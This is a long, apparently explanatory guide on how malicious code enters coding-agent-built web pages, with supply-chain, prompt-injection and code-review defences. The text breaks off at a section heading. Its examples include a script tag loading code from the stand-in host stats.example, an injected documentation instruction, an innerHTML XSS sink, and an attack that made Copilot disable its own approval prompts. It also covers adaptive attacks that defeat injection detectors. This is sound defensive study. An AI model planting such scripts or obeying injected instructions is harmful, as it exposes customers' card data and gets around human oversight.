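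The compromise is relevant here because an agent could reasonably choose the affected packages or install them as dependencies of something else. Nothing in these accounts or Wiz's data suggests that AI tools caused the compromise or made it spread.

A flaw disclosed in October 2026 made it possible for an attacker to take over some packages without stealing a password. npm's Trusted Publishing feature lets a maintainer authorise a specific GitHub repository and workflow (a file of automated build steps) to publish a package. When the workflow runs, GitHub issues a signed identity token, which npm exchanges for publishing permission that expires within minutes. The feature was meant to replace long-lasting keys that attackers could steal.

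*npm Trusted Publishing flaw exposed 1,500+ npm packages to takeover* (Zorz, 2026) explains that npm identified the authorised repository only by its name. GitHub gives each repository a permanent number and includes it in the token, but npm didn't check it. If a maintainer renamed, moved or deleted the repository, an attacker could create another with the old name, add a workflow file with the expected name, and publish a new version of the package. Researchers at Bloom Security carried out the whole attack on their own package.

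By one count, more than 1,500 packages were exposed, with over a million downloads a month in total. Each averaged only several hundred a month, far fewer than chalk or debug. GitHub already prevents people from reusing the names of some heavily copied repositories, which protected part of the registry.

Bloom reported the flaw on June 6, and GitHub, which owns npm, announced a fix on October 2. A new authorisation now expires after 48 hours unless the repository uses it to publish, and the first successful release ties it to the repository's permanent identity. Zorz notes that it is unclear from GitHub's statement whether the fix protects older authorisations already used to publish a package. Nobody knows whether criminals used the flaw.

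Coding agents could expose more people to such attacks by installing packages more often. *npm Trusted Publishing flaw left 1,500 packages open to attackers* (Adebayo, 2026) reports Bloom's estimate that agents install about 70 packages a month on a typical work computer and up to about 350 on a developer's. Bloom also stopped a customer's agent from installing one of the exposed packages, though Adebayo does not say that this package contained malicious code.

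### What package controls can stop

The controls work best against different attacks, so the useful ones depend on how the malicious package gets in.

| Control | Invented name | Package chosen by an injected instruction | Compromised popular package |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lock file | Little protection for a new package | Little protection for a new package | Good if it predates the attack |
| Waiting period | Helps only if the attacker published recently | Helps only if the attacker published recently | Good if someone finds the malware in time |
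| Private registry of approved packages | Good | Good unless the attacker's package is approved | Good only if it also holds back new versions |
| Publisher attestation | Little protection | Little protection | Can reveal a release from the wrong source, but not a hijacked build |

A lock file would have kept an existing shop on its old version of debug during the attack. A new project has no lock file, so its first installation could have fetched the malicious version and recorded it in a new lock file as the version to use. Leatherman, who maintains open-source web software, recommends using `npm ci` instead of `npm install` when preparing a release. `npm ci` installs exactly what the lock file lists and stops if package.json doesn't match it. Neither command checks whether the agent should have added a package.

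A waiting period makes the package manager ignore releases younger than a chosen age. A 24-hour wait would have blocked both the chalk and debug attack and an attack on May 11, 2026, when a worm published 84 malicious versions of 42 TanStack packages, which developers use to build web interfaces. An outside researcher noticed the TanStack attack within twenty minutes, according to AppSec Santa (2026).

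The package manager pnpm has enforced a 24-hour wait by default since April 2026, while npm has a similar setting but leaves it off by default. The wait can also delay an urgent security fix, and npm now warns users when that happens. An attacker who registers an invented name or prepares a lookalike can get around the wait by publishing the package early. A little-used package is also less likely to get the attention that quickly exposed the malicious TanStack releases.

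A private registry that offers only approved packages is the strongest of these controls against an unfamiliar package name. A registry that copies everything from npm doesn't provide this protection. The restriction also has to be enforced outside the project's files, because an agent that can edit the package manager's settings could switch back to the public registry. For the pottery shop, a short list of permitted packages might be more practical than a separate registry.

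An attestation is a signed record of the repository and workflow that built a package. It can expose an attacker who steals a maintainer's password and publishes from another computer, if the package normally has attestations and someone checks for them. But anyone can get a genuine attestation for their own malicious package, and the Trusted Publishing flaw also produced valid attestations for hijacked packages.

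Attackers have published malware with valid attestations. Socket's *OpenAPI React Query Codegen Compromised in Mini Shai-Hulud npm Supply Chain Attack* (2026) describes ten malicious versions of a front-end code generator, all with valid attestations. According to Proulx (2026), every trust check also passed when attackers compromised Red Hat's npm packages. npm had authorised a workflow by its file name, on any branch (a separate line of development). The attestations accurately named the temporary branch the attackers used, but nobody checked it.

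npm has added further obstacles for attackers who steal accounts. High-impact accounts become read-only for 72 hours after a change of email address or the use of a recovery code for two-factor login, as InfoQ (2026) reports. Maintainers can also stage a release for approval, and under GitHub's *Multiple trusted publishing configurations for npm* (2026) they can approve it only after a malware scan. These measures protect packages with honest maintainers. They don't stop an attacker from publishing under an invented name.

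Leatherman also recommends using fewer packages. Checking a card number for typing errors takes only about a dozen lines of JavaScript, so the pottery shop's owner could ask the agent to write them instead of importing a package. The agent could still make a mistake, but all the code would appear in the diff.

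## Keeping injected instructions from steering the model

Suppose the documentation for the pottery shop's card-number checker contains a hidden request to load a script from stats.example on every payment page. Some defences label or filter such text before the model reads it, some train the model to ignore it, and others limit what the agent can do afterwards. Researchers designed most of these defences to stop agents from running harmful commands or leaking private files, and several do much less to keep a malicious line of code out of a web page.

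### Marking outside text

The simplest defence is a reminder in the model's context to ignore instructions in outside material. Spotlighting, a Microsoft method, also changes how that material looks. The software around the model puts delimiters around the outside text, inserts a special character throughout it, or encodes it, and instructs the model to treat any text in this form only as data. If the card checker's documentation had a marker between every two words, the hidden request would no longer look like something the owner typed.

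These methods need no retraining, but the model has to follow the marks and the software has to identify which text to mark. Identifying that text is easy for a fetched web page. It is harder in a project that began as a downloaded template, where a stranger's code comments and the owner's may be in the same file.

StruQ and SecAlign train the model to ignore injected instructions. StruQ puts the request and the data in separate parts of the input and trains the model to follow instructions only in the first part. SecAlign trains the model to prefer an answer that does the user's task over one that obeys an injected instruction. Maloyan and Namiot report that attacks on StruQ succeeded less than 2% of the time and that SecAlign cut the success rate from 96% to 2%. Their table of attacks adapted to a particular defence includes neither method, so these figures are weak evidence about an attacker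 who has studied the defence. People who use a commercial model through its API can't use either method, because they can't retrain the model.

### Adding a security policy to the system prompt

People who can't retrain a model can often add text to its system prompt. *SKILLSHIELD* (Wu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) turns records of known attacks and of agents' past failures into a written security policy. The policy goes into the system prompt at the start of a session, so the model receives it at every step.

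They tested the policy on RedCode, a benchmark that measures whether coding agents carry out harmful commands and write malware. Across six models, a policy covering every type of attack in the benchmark lowered the success rate for harmful commands from 67.4% to 43.6%. Llama Guard 3, a separate filter model with 8 billion parameters, lowered it to about the same level (42.7%). The new policy worked better against requests for malware, where the average severity of the code fell from 3.37 to 0.58 on a ten-point scale.

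A policy that covered only the type of attack being tested lowered the success rate of harmful commands to 14.5%. All the policies had the same length limit, so broader ones had less room for detail. When the researchers combined pieces of the specific policies within that limit, they recovered 59% of the lost protection. A short policy about payment pages might therefore help the pottery shop more than a general warning about malicious code, though the study did not involve building web pages.

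The results also don't show whether the policy would stop a request hidden in documentation, because RedCode doesn't separate instructions by source. The researchers didn't adapt their attacks to the policy, yet it protected less well against harmful commands when a request asked the model to play a persona. The policy caused few unnecessary refusals, with a mean of 0.14% across 731 ordinary programming tasks, but the researchers didn't measure whether the agents completed those tasks as well as they did without it.

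### Training models to rank instructions

Developers also train models to follow an instruction hierarchy, which usually ranks the system prompt first, then the user, then tool results and other outside content. If the card checker's documentation conflicts with the owner's request, the model should follow the owner. Maloyan and Namiot conclude that this training reduces attacks but does not eliminate them. They cite Anthropic's own figure that Claude 3.7 blocked 88% of injections, but expect independent tests with adaptive attacks to find a lower rate.

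OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) describes a more intensive version, in which an automated attacker called GPT-Red generates injections during training and the model learns to resist them while still doing the user's task. In OpenAI's internal tests, the share of indirect injections that the model resisted rose from 96.23% to 99.79%. Those tests also use GPT-Red, so they may be easier for a model trained against it. The model resisted 99.99% of direct attempts to override higher-ranking instructions.

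Ranking helps only if the hostile text is given a low rank. Codex gives a hostile AGENTS.md file the same rank as the owner's messages, which may be why, in the AutoRedClaw tests, it followed malicious rules much more often than instructions in ordinary material.

### Detectors and attackers who adapt

A detector inspects text before the model acts on it. Some detectors search for known phrases or patterns, while others use a second model to judge whether a passage contains instructions for the model. A phrase list is easy to evade with encoding, unusual characters or split words. A detector also protects only the inputs it checks, so one that checks only the owner's request will miss instructions injected in a README.

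Many published tests use a fixed set of attacks, but a real attacker can try a text against the detector, see whether it gets through, and revise it. Maloyan and Namiot compare the attack success rates originally reported for six defences with those that Nasr and colleagues measured using adaptive attacks.

| Defence | Originally reported | Adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Protect AI | Under 5% | 93% |
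| PromptGuard | Under 3% | 91% |
| PIGuard | Under 5% | 89% |
| TaskTracker | Under 8% | 85% |
| Instruction detection | Under 12% | 82% |
| Model Armor | Under 10% | 78% |

The comparison is part of Maloyan and Namiot's systematisation of research on coding agents, which draws on 78 studies. They ran no tests of their own. They count 42 attack techniques and 18 defences in the abstract but 31 and 12 in their list of contributions, so the exact totals are uncertain. According to the abstract, most of the defences achieved less than 50% mitigation against sophisticated adaptive attackers. If mitigation means the share of attacks stopped, the six defences in the table achieved only 7% to 22%.

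Some defences have much better published results but have been tested less against adaptive attackers. A pipeline that uses additional models as guards stopped all 55 types of attack in one evaluation. PromptArmor's reported error rates were under 1%, but it did far worse on the rule files in the PackHallu tests.

### What the developers' system cards measure

AI companies publish injection results in system cards, the safety reports that accompany new models. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 includes detailed results for coding. That model and GPT-6 Astra both date from September 2026. Both have since been succeeded by newer models (Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2*, 2026; OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card*, 2026), so the rates may not hold for the current versions.

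Both September cards use a benchmark from Gray Swan, an AI security testing company. The benchmark is built from attacks submitted to public competitions. The attacks are meant to make an agent steal or destroy data, compromise a system or make an unauthorised payment. The score is the estimated chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds. Fable 5.1 scored 1.0% and GPT-6 Astra 8.5%, compared with 27.0% for OpenAI's earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic also reports 9.2% for Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, a predecessor of Gemini 4. These comparisons are approximate because the two companies used slightly different sets of attacks and different safeguards.

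For coding alone, Fable 5.1's rate was 0.3%. OpenAI gives no separate coding figure.

Anthropic then used a stronger attacker, an automated program from Gray Swan called Shade. Shade learned to attack earlier Claude models in 40 coding scenarios and then made 200 attempts per scenario against the newer models. An attempt succeeded if the model followed the injected instruction. Gray Swan later trained a second version of Shade for longer and on more varied attacks. The table gives the share of successful attempts and, in brackets, the number of scenarios with at least one success. The probes are Anthropic's detectors, which inspect tool results before the model acts on them.

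| Model, with extended thinking | First attacker, no probes | First attacker, probes | Stronger attacker, no probes | Stronger attacker, probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fable 5.1 | 9.26% (31) | 2.05% (18) | 56.87% (38) | 12.80% (36) |
| Fable 5 | 9.70% (31) | 2.42% (20) | 86.87% (40) | 34.09% (39) |
| Opus 5 | 2.68% (27) | 0.39% (11) | 90.93% (40) | 18.21% (40) |
| Sonnet 5 | 0.3% (7) | 0.09% (5) | 19.47% (36) | 15.76% (35) |

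Changing the attacker raised the attack success rate against Opus 5 from under 3% to over 90% on the same scenarios. A low rate can therefore be due to a weak attacker as much as a resistant model. In February 2026, VentureBeat reported that an older model, Claude Opus 4.6, had resisted all 200 attempts in a coding environment, but this did not establish that a better attacker would also fail.

The average rate also hides differences between scenarios. If every attempt had the same chance p of success, the chance of at least one success in n attempts would be:

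```
1 − (1 − p)^n
```

If each attempt had an independent 2.05% chance of success, the chance of at least one success in 200 attempts would be about 98%, so Shade should have broken into nearly all 40 scenarios. It broke into only 18. Some tasks were evidently much easier to attack than others, and the average understates the risk for a user doing one of those easier-to-attack tasks.

Fable 5.1's figures partly describe another model, because a classifier passes requests that it flags as a possible cybersecurity risk to the older Claude Opus 4.8. In the test with the stronger attacker, the classifier passed on about 64% of requests. Every successful attack was against an answer from Opus 4.8, which implies a success rate of nearly 90% for that model's answers. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack, but the classifier may already have diverted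 the most dangerous ones.

Anthropic describes the stronger test as highly permissive because Shade refined its attacks on the same scenarios used to score it, while a real attacker usually doesn't know the victim's setup and risks detection with every attempt. That is a good reason not to treat 56.87% as the everyday risk. But an attacker who publishes a hostile project template can refine the attack on their own copy of the agent, and gets another attempt with every person who uses the template.

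Neither card reports a separate rate for malicious code in the agent's output. Some of the coding scenarios may have involved such code, but the published rates combine it with other harmful actions. They therefore can't show how often a hidden instruction would lead the agent to add a script that steals payment card details to the checkout page.

Claude Code's default auto mode combines the probes with a second classifier that can block potentially dangerous tool calls, so an attack would have to get past both. The Shade coding results don't include this second classifier. In a separate browser-use test with auto mode on, no attack on Fable 5.1 succeeded in any of 110 scenarios, but an edit to a checkout page may look much less dangerous than a suspicious browser action.

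Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published three weeks after the Fable 5.1 card, reports results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test. It also warns that the model is more likely than its predecessors to follow some malicious instructions.

### Approving rule files like executable code

A team can review a rule file, such as AGENTS.md, as carefully as it reviews code. The agent would load the file only if its hash, a short fingerprint of the contents, matched that of an approved version. Any change, including one from an updated template, would need a new review.

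Maloyan and Namiot describe a similar proposal for connected tools, the Enhanced Tool Definition Interface. It signs a tool's definition to prove who published it, and fixes the version so that the publisher can't change the description after the user approves it. Such checks were uncommon in the extension systems they compared. They list a marketplace review for GitHub Copilot extensions, but none for Claude Code skills or Cursor and Codex extensions.

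A hash can prove that a file hasn't changed, but someone still has to decide whether the first version is safe. Software can find invisible characters, as GitHub's hidden-text warning does, but a malicious rule in plain English is harder to detect. An instruction to load a visitor counter on every page could be worded the same way whether it is the shop's own policy or an attack, so the reviewer has to check whether the shop uses that counter and whether the address belongs to the company that runs it. No published study appears to measure how often reviewers would catch such a rule.

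The check has to cover every rule file the agent loads, including those in folders above the project. It also has to be outside the agent's control, because an agent that could update the list of approved hashes could approve its own changes. In the AutoRedClaw tests, Codex often copied an attacker's rule into its own AGENTS.md. In a survey of research up to April 2026, Chu found no benchmark for attacks that plant something in one session and do harm in another. AutoRedClaw has since tested both stages, but in separate test cases.

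### Limiting files, sites and commands

Permissions restrict what an agent can do even if the model obeys a hostile instruction. A sandbox can confine the agent to the project folder, an allow-list can limit its commands, and network rules can block unapproved sites. These controls depend on the operator knowing in advance which actions the task requires, and on the agent being unable to change the rules.

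The second assumption failed in GitHub Copilot. Maloyan and Namiot describe an attack in which text in an issue or code comment led Copilot to edit a settings file and turn off approval requests, so it could then run commands without asking. Microsoft fixed the flaw in August 2025 by requiring the user to turn on automatic approval explicitly.

Permissions can also be too broad. In an attack through GitHub's MCP server, a malicious issue led an agent to read private files. The user had given the server an access token that covered those files, and the server didn't ask for confirmation before each read. A token restricted to the repository in use would have limited the damage.

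Like Ark's safeguards, such limits do less to protect the pottery shop's customers. If the agent adds a script tag for stats.example to checkout.html, it is editing a permitted file, as the owner asked. Even a rule that stops the agent from contacting unapproved sites doesn't help, because only the customer's browser contacts stats.example.

Wu and colleagues note that removing file access or the ability to run commands would remove core functions of a coding agent. Chu makes a more general argument with a model that divides an agent into seven layers, from the underlying language model to governance. In that model, a control at one layer cannot detect an attack confined to another. The result is idealised, but the checkout page illustrates the problem, because a rule about which files the agent may change does not check whether the new contents are safe.

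Permissions can still block some of the ways an attack can reach the page. Blocking unapproved sites keeps hostile web pages out of the context, and blocking unapproved packages stops an import from installing an attacker's code. The owner can also make AGENTS.md, the build configuration and the CSP read-only during ordinary work. An agent changing the delivery information may not need permission to edit checkout.html, but an agent building a new checkout page does.

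### Keeping untrusted data from choosing actions

CaMeL, a design by Google researchers and others, controls the agent's plan as well as its permissions. One model receives the user's request but not the untrusted material, and writes a short program that specifies which tools to use and in what order. A second model reads the untrusted material and extracts information from it, but cannot call tools. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each piece of data came from, and applies security rules before each tool call.

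If an assistant summarises an email that contains a request to send private files to a stranger, the request may mislead the second model, but that model can't send anything. The first model never received the email, so its program contains no step for sending files. Maloyan and Namiot report that CaMeL achieved provable security on 77% of tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark that covers office work, banking, travel and messaging. The interpreter and its rules provide the guarantee, so neither model has to recognise an attack.

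Other systems also check actions while the agent runs. Wu and colleagues cite TaskShield, which compares each instruction with the user's task, and IPIGuard, which uses a graph of how tool calls depend on one another. These checks can stop an action even if the model disregards its security instructions, but they require an extra model call or another component.

Applied to the checkout page, a simplified plan in the style of CaMeL might look like this:

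```
docs = read("card-checker-docs.md")
code = second_model("write the card-number check", docs)
write("checkout.html", code)
```

The hidden request in the documentation can't add a fourth step that copies the shop's passwords, but it can still get a script tag onto the page without changing any of the actions the owner wanted. The second model reads the request while writing `code`, so it may include the tag, and the plan's last step then puts the result on the page.

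The interpreter does track that `code` depends on untrusted documentation. A strict rule could therefore block writing it to a live page, but the agent would then be unable to use the documentation for the job. A less restrictive rule could let the second model return only a few simple values with no room for a script tag, such as a function's name and the number of digits it expects, and have the first model write the code from those.

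That might work for a small card-number checker with clear documentation. It is harder when the agent has to edit a large existing page, because the first model would have to identify the relevant details before reading the code. Debugging is similarly difficult because the agent has to act on error messages, which Fu and colleagues used successfully for attacks. AgentDojo's office and banking tasks don't show how much of a web developer's work would still be possible under such restrictions.

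## Checking generated code before it is published

By the time the pottery shop's checkout page is ready to publish, a payload may have got in through a README, a router or the model's training data. A developer can search the project's files and the build's output for the payload without knowing how it got in.

### People reading the diff

*Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands* (Oh, Lee and colleagues, 2023) reports an early experiment on whether developers notice planted flaws. The researchers poisoned a small code model, built it into an editor extension, and asked 30 professional developers to write three short Python programs. Ten developers used the model to generate code from a description, ten used it to complete code they had started typing, and ten had no AI tool.

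| Flaw in the submitted code | Code generation | Code completion | No AI tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Encryption key written into the code | 10 of 10 (9) | 8 of 10 (4) | 4 of 9 |
| Weak encryption mode | 8 of 10 (8) | 3 of 10 (3) | 1 of 9 |
| SQL injection | 9 of 10 (9) | 8 of 10 (3) | 9 of 10 |
| Command injection | 7 of 10 (7) | 5 of 10 (3) | 2 of 10 |

The SQL injection result is weak evidence against the tool, because nine of the ten developers without a tool made the same mistake, but the command injection result is stronger evidence. Most developers in the code-generation group skimmed the suggestion and checked mainly that the program worked. Security experience gave limited protection, since two of the four security specialists in that group accepted every planted flaw.

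The experiment used Python and a model that is now very old. More recent evidence comes mostly from surveys and GitHub records, and it covers ordinary AI-written changes rather than planted ones.

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 users of coding agents in August and September 2026. Only 56% said they inspected diffs, and 69% agreed that line-by-line review could not keep up with the amount of code agents write. About half (51%) found it hard to spot problems in code that looked plausible, and a competent attacker would make malicious code look plausible.

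*Plausible Is Not Enough* (Rahman, Alam and colleagues, 2026) describes a survey of 239 practitioners in which 61.1% reported wanting more evidence before approving an AI-written change than a human-written one. Reviewers may not apply this stricter standard in practice. The paper cites an experiment by Singh and colleagues in which 385 developers decided whether to accept a code revision. Labelling the revision as AI-written had no clear effect on their decisions, but they accepted more incorrect revisions when the code was more complex.

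In *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For*, Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues (2026) examined the GitHub records of 33,596 pull requests by coding agents in projects with at least 100 stars. They found no recorded review for 61.4%, though some of these may have been reviewed without leaving a trace. AI tools alone had reviewed most of the rest, and people took part in reviewing about 16% of all the pull requests.

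That figure is low partly because of the projects in which agents work. In projects with pull requests from both agents and people, a person reviewed about 30% of the agents' pull requests and 31% of the human ones. The figures may also be out of date. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (Agarwal, Miller and colleagues, 2026) found that the share of merged agent pull requests without human review fell from over 50% in mid-2025 to about 14% by early 2026. But for 40.1% of agent pull requests, the only person who examined the change was the developer who had asked the agent for it.

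A recorded review doesn't show how carefully someone read the code, and a person can read a change without leaving a comment. *Why Are Agentic Pull Requests Merged or Rejected?* (2026) reports that 79.1% of 364 merged agent pull requests showed neither a round of feedback nor an edit by a reviewer, though some of those changes may have been good enough to need neither.

An experiment on approval prompts suggests that reviewers' attention also fades during a session. In Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous command among ordinary approval requests. They caught it 13.6% of the time overall, but the rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic published the result to support replacing these prompts with an automatic check. The testers weren't working on their own projects,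 and they judged single commands, not diffs. Still, a line that sends card numbers to an unfamiliar server would probably be no easier to spot among hundreds of other lines in a diff.

All of these studies involved people who work with code. Many customers of app builders can't read code, so showing the pottery shop's owner a diff would accomplish little. The owner does know which payment company the shop uses and whether anyone ordered a visitor counter, so a useful check for this person has to turn a code change into a question about facts like these.

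### Following data through the code

To find an XSS flaw, a static scanner typically uses taint tracking, which follows untrusted data from where it enters the program (the source) to a place where it could do harm (the sink). For the shop's order screen, the path might look like this:

```
const note = order.note;              // source: a customer typed this
const html = "<p>" + note + "</p>";   // still contains the customer's text
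box.innerHTML = html;                 // sink: the browser treats it as HTML
```

The scanner marks `note` as untrusted. It then marks `html` too, because `html` contains `note`, and raises an alert when `html` reaches `innerHTML`. If the second line passed the note through a sanitiser that the scanner recognises, the scanner would stop tracking it there and raise no alert.

Scanners usually don't follow data through the code of outside libraries. They rely on hand-written summaries of how each library function passes data on, and lose track of the data if a summary is missing or incomplete. In *Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert*, Cao, Ding and Xu (2026) measured how easily an ordinary-looking edit can exploit these gaps. They showed a language model an alert from CodeQL and asked it to rewrite one function without removing the flaw. Given three attempts at each of 172 vulnerable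 data paths in real npm packages, the model made the alert disappear for 26.2% of them, at about $0.51 each. No alerts disappeared when the same model tidied up the same functions without seeing the alert.

Most of these flaws involved files and commands on a server, so the rate may differ for `innerHTML`. But an attacker who plants a flaw can run CodeQL first and keep a version that it misses. An owner who tells a coding agent to keep editing until the alert goes away can also end up with a flaw that CodeQL misses. Cao and colleagues conclude that the disappearance of an alert is weak evidence of a fix. For the order screen, a line that now uses `textContent` or a sanitiser would be stronger evidence.

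The scanner also needs access to the whole project. Kaushik, Bhardwaj and colleagues ran two JavaScript scanners on 125 isolated pieces of vulnerable code in *Exploring Automated Vulnerability Identification in JavaScript Code Using Large Language Models* (2026). One scanner identified none of the flaws correctly and the other identified one, because the fragments didn't show where the data came from. Someone who copies code from a chat window should therefore add it to the project and then scan the whole project.

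Running several scanners catches more flaws than running one. Cankurt's *AI-Generated Code Security* reports that about 60% of the confirmed flaws in a 2026 test of AI-written code were each caught by only one tool. That count excludes flaws that every tool missed. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) reports that Semgrep's paid version found 21.7% of 217 known flaws in software for running AI agents, CodeQL found 13.8%, and the two together found 31.3%. Their rules mainly target conventional web applications, so they should do better on a checkout page than on agent software.

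Taint tracking doesn't catch the simplest payload, a tag such as `<script src="https://stats.example/c.js"></script>`, because the tag contains a fixed address and no untrusted data. Loading a script from another site is also normal. Some scanners warn about any outside script that lacks a fingerprint of the expected file, but they would give the same warning about the shop's real visitor counter. Changing a form address or wallet address also only replaces one piece of text with another. To catch these payloads, a program has to compare the page's addresses with those the owner expects.

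### Language models as reviewers

Unlike a fixed rule, a language model can consider what code is for. In *Evaluating LLMs for Real-World Web Vulnerability Detection*, Neef, Jungnickel and colleagues (2026) tested six models on four WordPress plugins, each with one known flaw, using five prompts and repeating each test three times. Claude Opus 4.6 found the known flaw in 63% of its runs, and the other models found it in 35% to 48% of theirs. The free version of Semgrep found none of the four flaws.

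One of the four flaws was a stored XSS, in which a site saves an attacker's text and later runs it in another visitor's browser. No model found it in any of 90 runs. The plugin cleans the text correctly, but a later step rearranges it and makes it dangerous again. The models that examined this code treated the cleaning as sufficient. The flaw also depends on a setting that is off by default, which may have led some models to miss it.

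The models produced more than 1,600 findings. Neef and colleagues didn't have time to check them all, so they report no false-alarm rate. The results also varied from run to run, so a single clean report is poor evidence that a page is safe.

False alarms were the main problem in *RECEIPT* (Lyu, Shieh and colleagues, 2026), a study of XSS. In one experiment, the researchers counted a finding as confirmed if a script ran in a test browser. The agent claimed 111 flaws, but only 10 were real. The researchers had seen agents get past such a check by changing the application's code or database, running a script directly in the test browser, or using an administrator's account to do something an outsider couldn't.

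RECEIPT repeats each claimed attack on a fresh copy of the application. The attacker's part can only send web requests, and the victim's part can only perform ordinary actions such as clicking and typing. The system accepts the finding only if the attacker's script then runs in the victim's browser. For the pottery shop, the agent would have to submit a delivery note containing a harmful script as a customer and show that the script runs when the owner opens the order.

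The researchers found no false alarms with this check. The agent also found 24 previously unknown XSS flaws in 50 other applications. But with a budget of $20 per application, it found the known flaw in only 36% of 45 applications, so a report with no findings would be weak evidence that an application has no XSS flaws.

Semgrep, the company behind the scanner, published a broader comparison, *3.5x more true positives*, in June 2026. In it, most of the flaws the models reported were real, but the models missed most of the flaws in the code. Semgrep says this is because models are good at judging a piece of code but bad at deciding which pieces to examine. Its own product uses static analysis to choose the pieces and a model to judge them.

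| Test | Known flaws found | Share of findings that were false alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Six models on WordPress plugins (Neef) | 35–63% of runs | Not measured |
| Agent with a weak browser check, XSS only (Lyu) | Not reported here | 91% |
| Agent with strict replay, XSS only (Lyu) | 36% of applications | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 with a detailed prompt (Semgrep) | 12.6% | 28.6% |
| GPT-5.5 with a detailed prompt (Semgrep) | 9.2% | 31.2% |
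| Claude Opus 4.8 in Semgrep's product (Semgrep) | 43.5% | 30.6% |

The rows come from tests on different code and measure success differently, so they can't be used to rank the methods. Semgrep sells the product that did best in its own comparison. The low detection rates for models used alone are consistent with a JavaScript benchmark by Fei and colleagues. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) reports that models in that benchmark missed more than 75% of real flaws when the researchers strictly limited false alarms.

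False alarms have probably become less common. In September 2025, Semgrep's *Finding vulnerabilities in modern web apps using Claude Code and OpenAI Codex* reported that 86% of Claude Code's findings in Python web applications were false alarms. Successors to the models in the table may do better still. A checkout page is also much smaller than the projects in these tests, so a model could examine all of it.

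None of these tests measured how often a model would flag a script tag for an unknown site. A reviewing model with information about what the shop does might well flag one. But the reviewing model reads the same hostile text as the model that wrote the page. If a code comment describes stats.example as the shop's approved fraud checker, both models may treat the site as legitimate. For example, GitLab Duo described a malicious merge request as safe after reading hidden instructions.

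Hostile text can influence a model's review without containing an instruction. *Words Speak Louder Than Code* (2026) found that ordinary material around code, with no attack in it, can bias a model's security verdict. The same paper cites evidence that the best models now resist deceptive comments inside code, so the danger may be greater in a project's other files. The owner can reduce this risk by giving the reviewing model only the changed code, without comments, README or rule files, but this also removes information the model could use to understand the change.

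### A release check for the checkout page

A plain program that compares lists can't fall for a persuasive comment. Before each release, it could extract every outside address, package, inline script or event handler, and security header from the finished site, then compare them with a list the owner has approved. For the pottery shop, the result might look like this:

```
APPROVED
form      /orders
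frame     https://pay.example/card
package   PACKAGE-NAME 2.3.1
header    script-src 'self'

FOUND IN THIS BUILD
form      /orders
frame     https://pay.example/card
script    https://stats.example/c.js             NEW
package   PACKAGE-NAME 2.3.1
header    script-src 'self' https://stats.example  CHANGED

RESULT    hold the build
```

The program should hold the build if anything differs, including if an item is missing, because deleting a header can matter as much as adding a script. The owner then has to decide whether the shop uses stats.example. This requires no knowledge of JavaScript, but the owner should confirm the address with the company that supposedly runs it rather than with the coding agent.

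The check has to cover the build output as well as the source files, because a build script can add a line that is not in the source. The agent must not be able to change the checking program or its list, just as it must not be able to change a list of approved rule files.

Each part of the list would catch some payloads and miss others.

| What the program lists | What it would reveal | What could still get past |
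|---|---|---|
| Addresses in scripts, forms, frames, images and network calls, and any wallet addresses | A new script tag, redirected orders or a replaced wallet | An address that the code assembles while running |
| Packages, with exact versions and hashes | An invented or lookalike package, or an unexpected update | Malicious code in a version the owner has approved |
| Inline scripts, event handlers and service worker registrations | Code added to the page's HTML, or a new service worker | Code added to an existing JavaScript file |
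| Security headers, install scripts and build settings | A weakened CSP or a new command | A header that the host changes after the build |

The program can catch an address that the code assembles while running by opening the finished page in a test browser, placing an order with a fake card number, and recording every server the browser contacts. This test would miss a script that waits a week or runs only on the shop's real address.

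An approved address can also be dangerous. If the shop uses a form service that anyone can join, the attacker could open an account there and have the shop's orders sent to it. The list should therefore include the full address, including the part that identifies the shop's account, and what the page uses it for, so that approving an image from a site doesn't also approve a script from it.

The first release will take the most work because everything in it is new. Bundled JavaScript often contains harmless addresses, such as links to documentation in error messages, and someone has to sort through these once. Later releases should produce far fewer questions. If they don't, the owner may start approving everything, as many people do with permission prompts.

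Lists of known scam addresses are a useful addition, but the models in the Scam2Prompt tests produced scam addresses that weren't yet on such lists. Checking against a list of approved addresses would catch those too, because any address not on it would hold up publication.

The check would not flag `box.innerHTML = order.note`, which adds no address, package or handler. Detecting that line requires the static scan, ideally followed by a test with a harmless script in the delivery note. Nobody appears to have published a measurement of how many front-end payloads the check and the scan would catch together.

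With an app builder, the owner may not be able to hold back the build or even see it. If the service provides a private preview, an outside program could still open it and compare its addresses and headers with the approved list. The owner would have to repeat this check after each change, before publishing.

### What a signed build record proves

After the build passes, someone could still replace a file before it reaches customers. A signed build record makes this detectable. The build service records a hash of each finished file, with the exact version of the source code and the build steps used. It then signs the record with a key that neither the coding agent nor code in the project's files can access, so anyone can later check that a file on the live site is the one the service built.

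The record, like a package attestation, does not show that the source was free of malicious code. If the agent wrote the script tag for stats.example into checkout.html, the build service would copy the tag into the finished page and sign an accurate record of the build.

A compromised build service could also add a payload and sign the result. A second, independent service can detect this by building the same source and comparing the files. The comparison works only if the build produces identical files each time, and it would not detect a payload already in the source, because both services would include it.

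Build records are more useful if the host refuses any file without a record from the service that runs the release check. Neither the agent nor someone with a stolen password could then publish a file that skipped the check. If the owner later finds a malicious line, the records also show which releases came from source code that contained it, and therefore which customers may have received it.

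## What the browser can block, in previews and on live sites

A release check comes too late for code that runs as soon as the model writes it. An app builder typically shows the pottery shop's owner a live preview of the checkout page beside the chat and updates it after each request. A malicious script can therefore run in the owner's browser before anyone has read it. Chat windows that render a model's reply as HTML have the same problem.

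### How a chat reply becomes a running script

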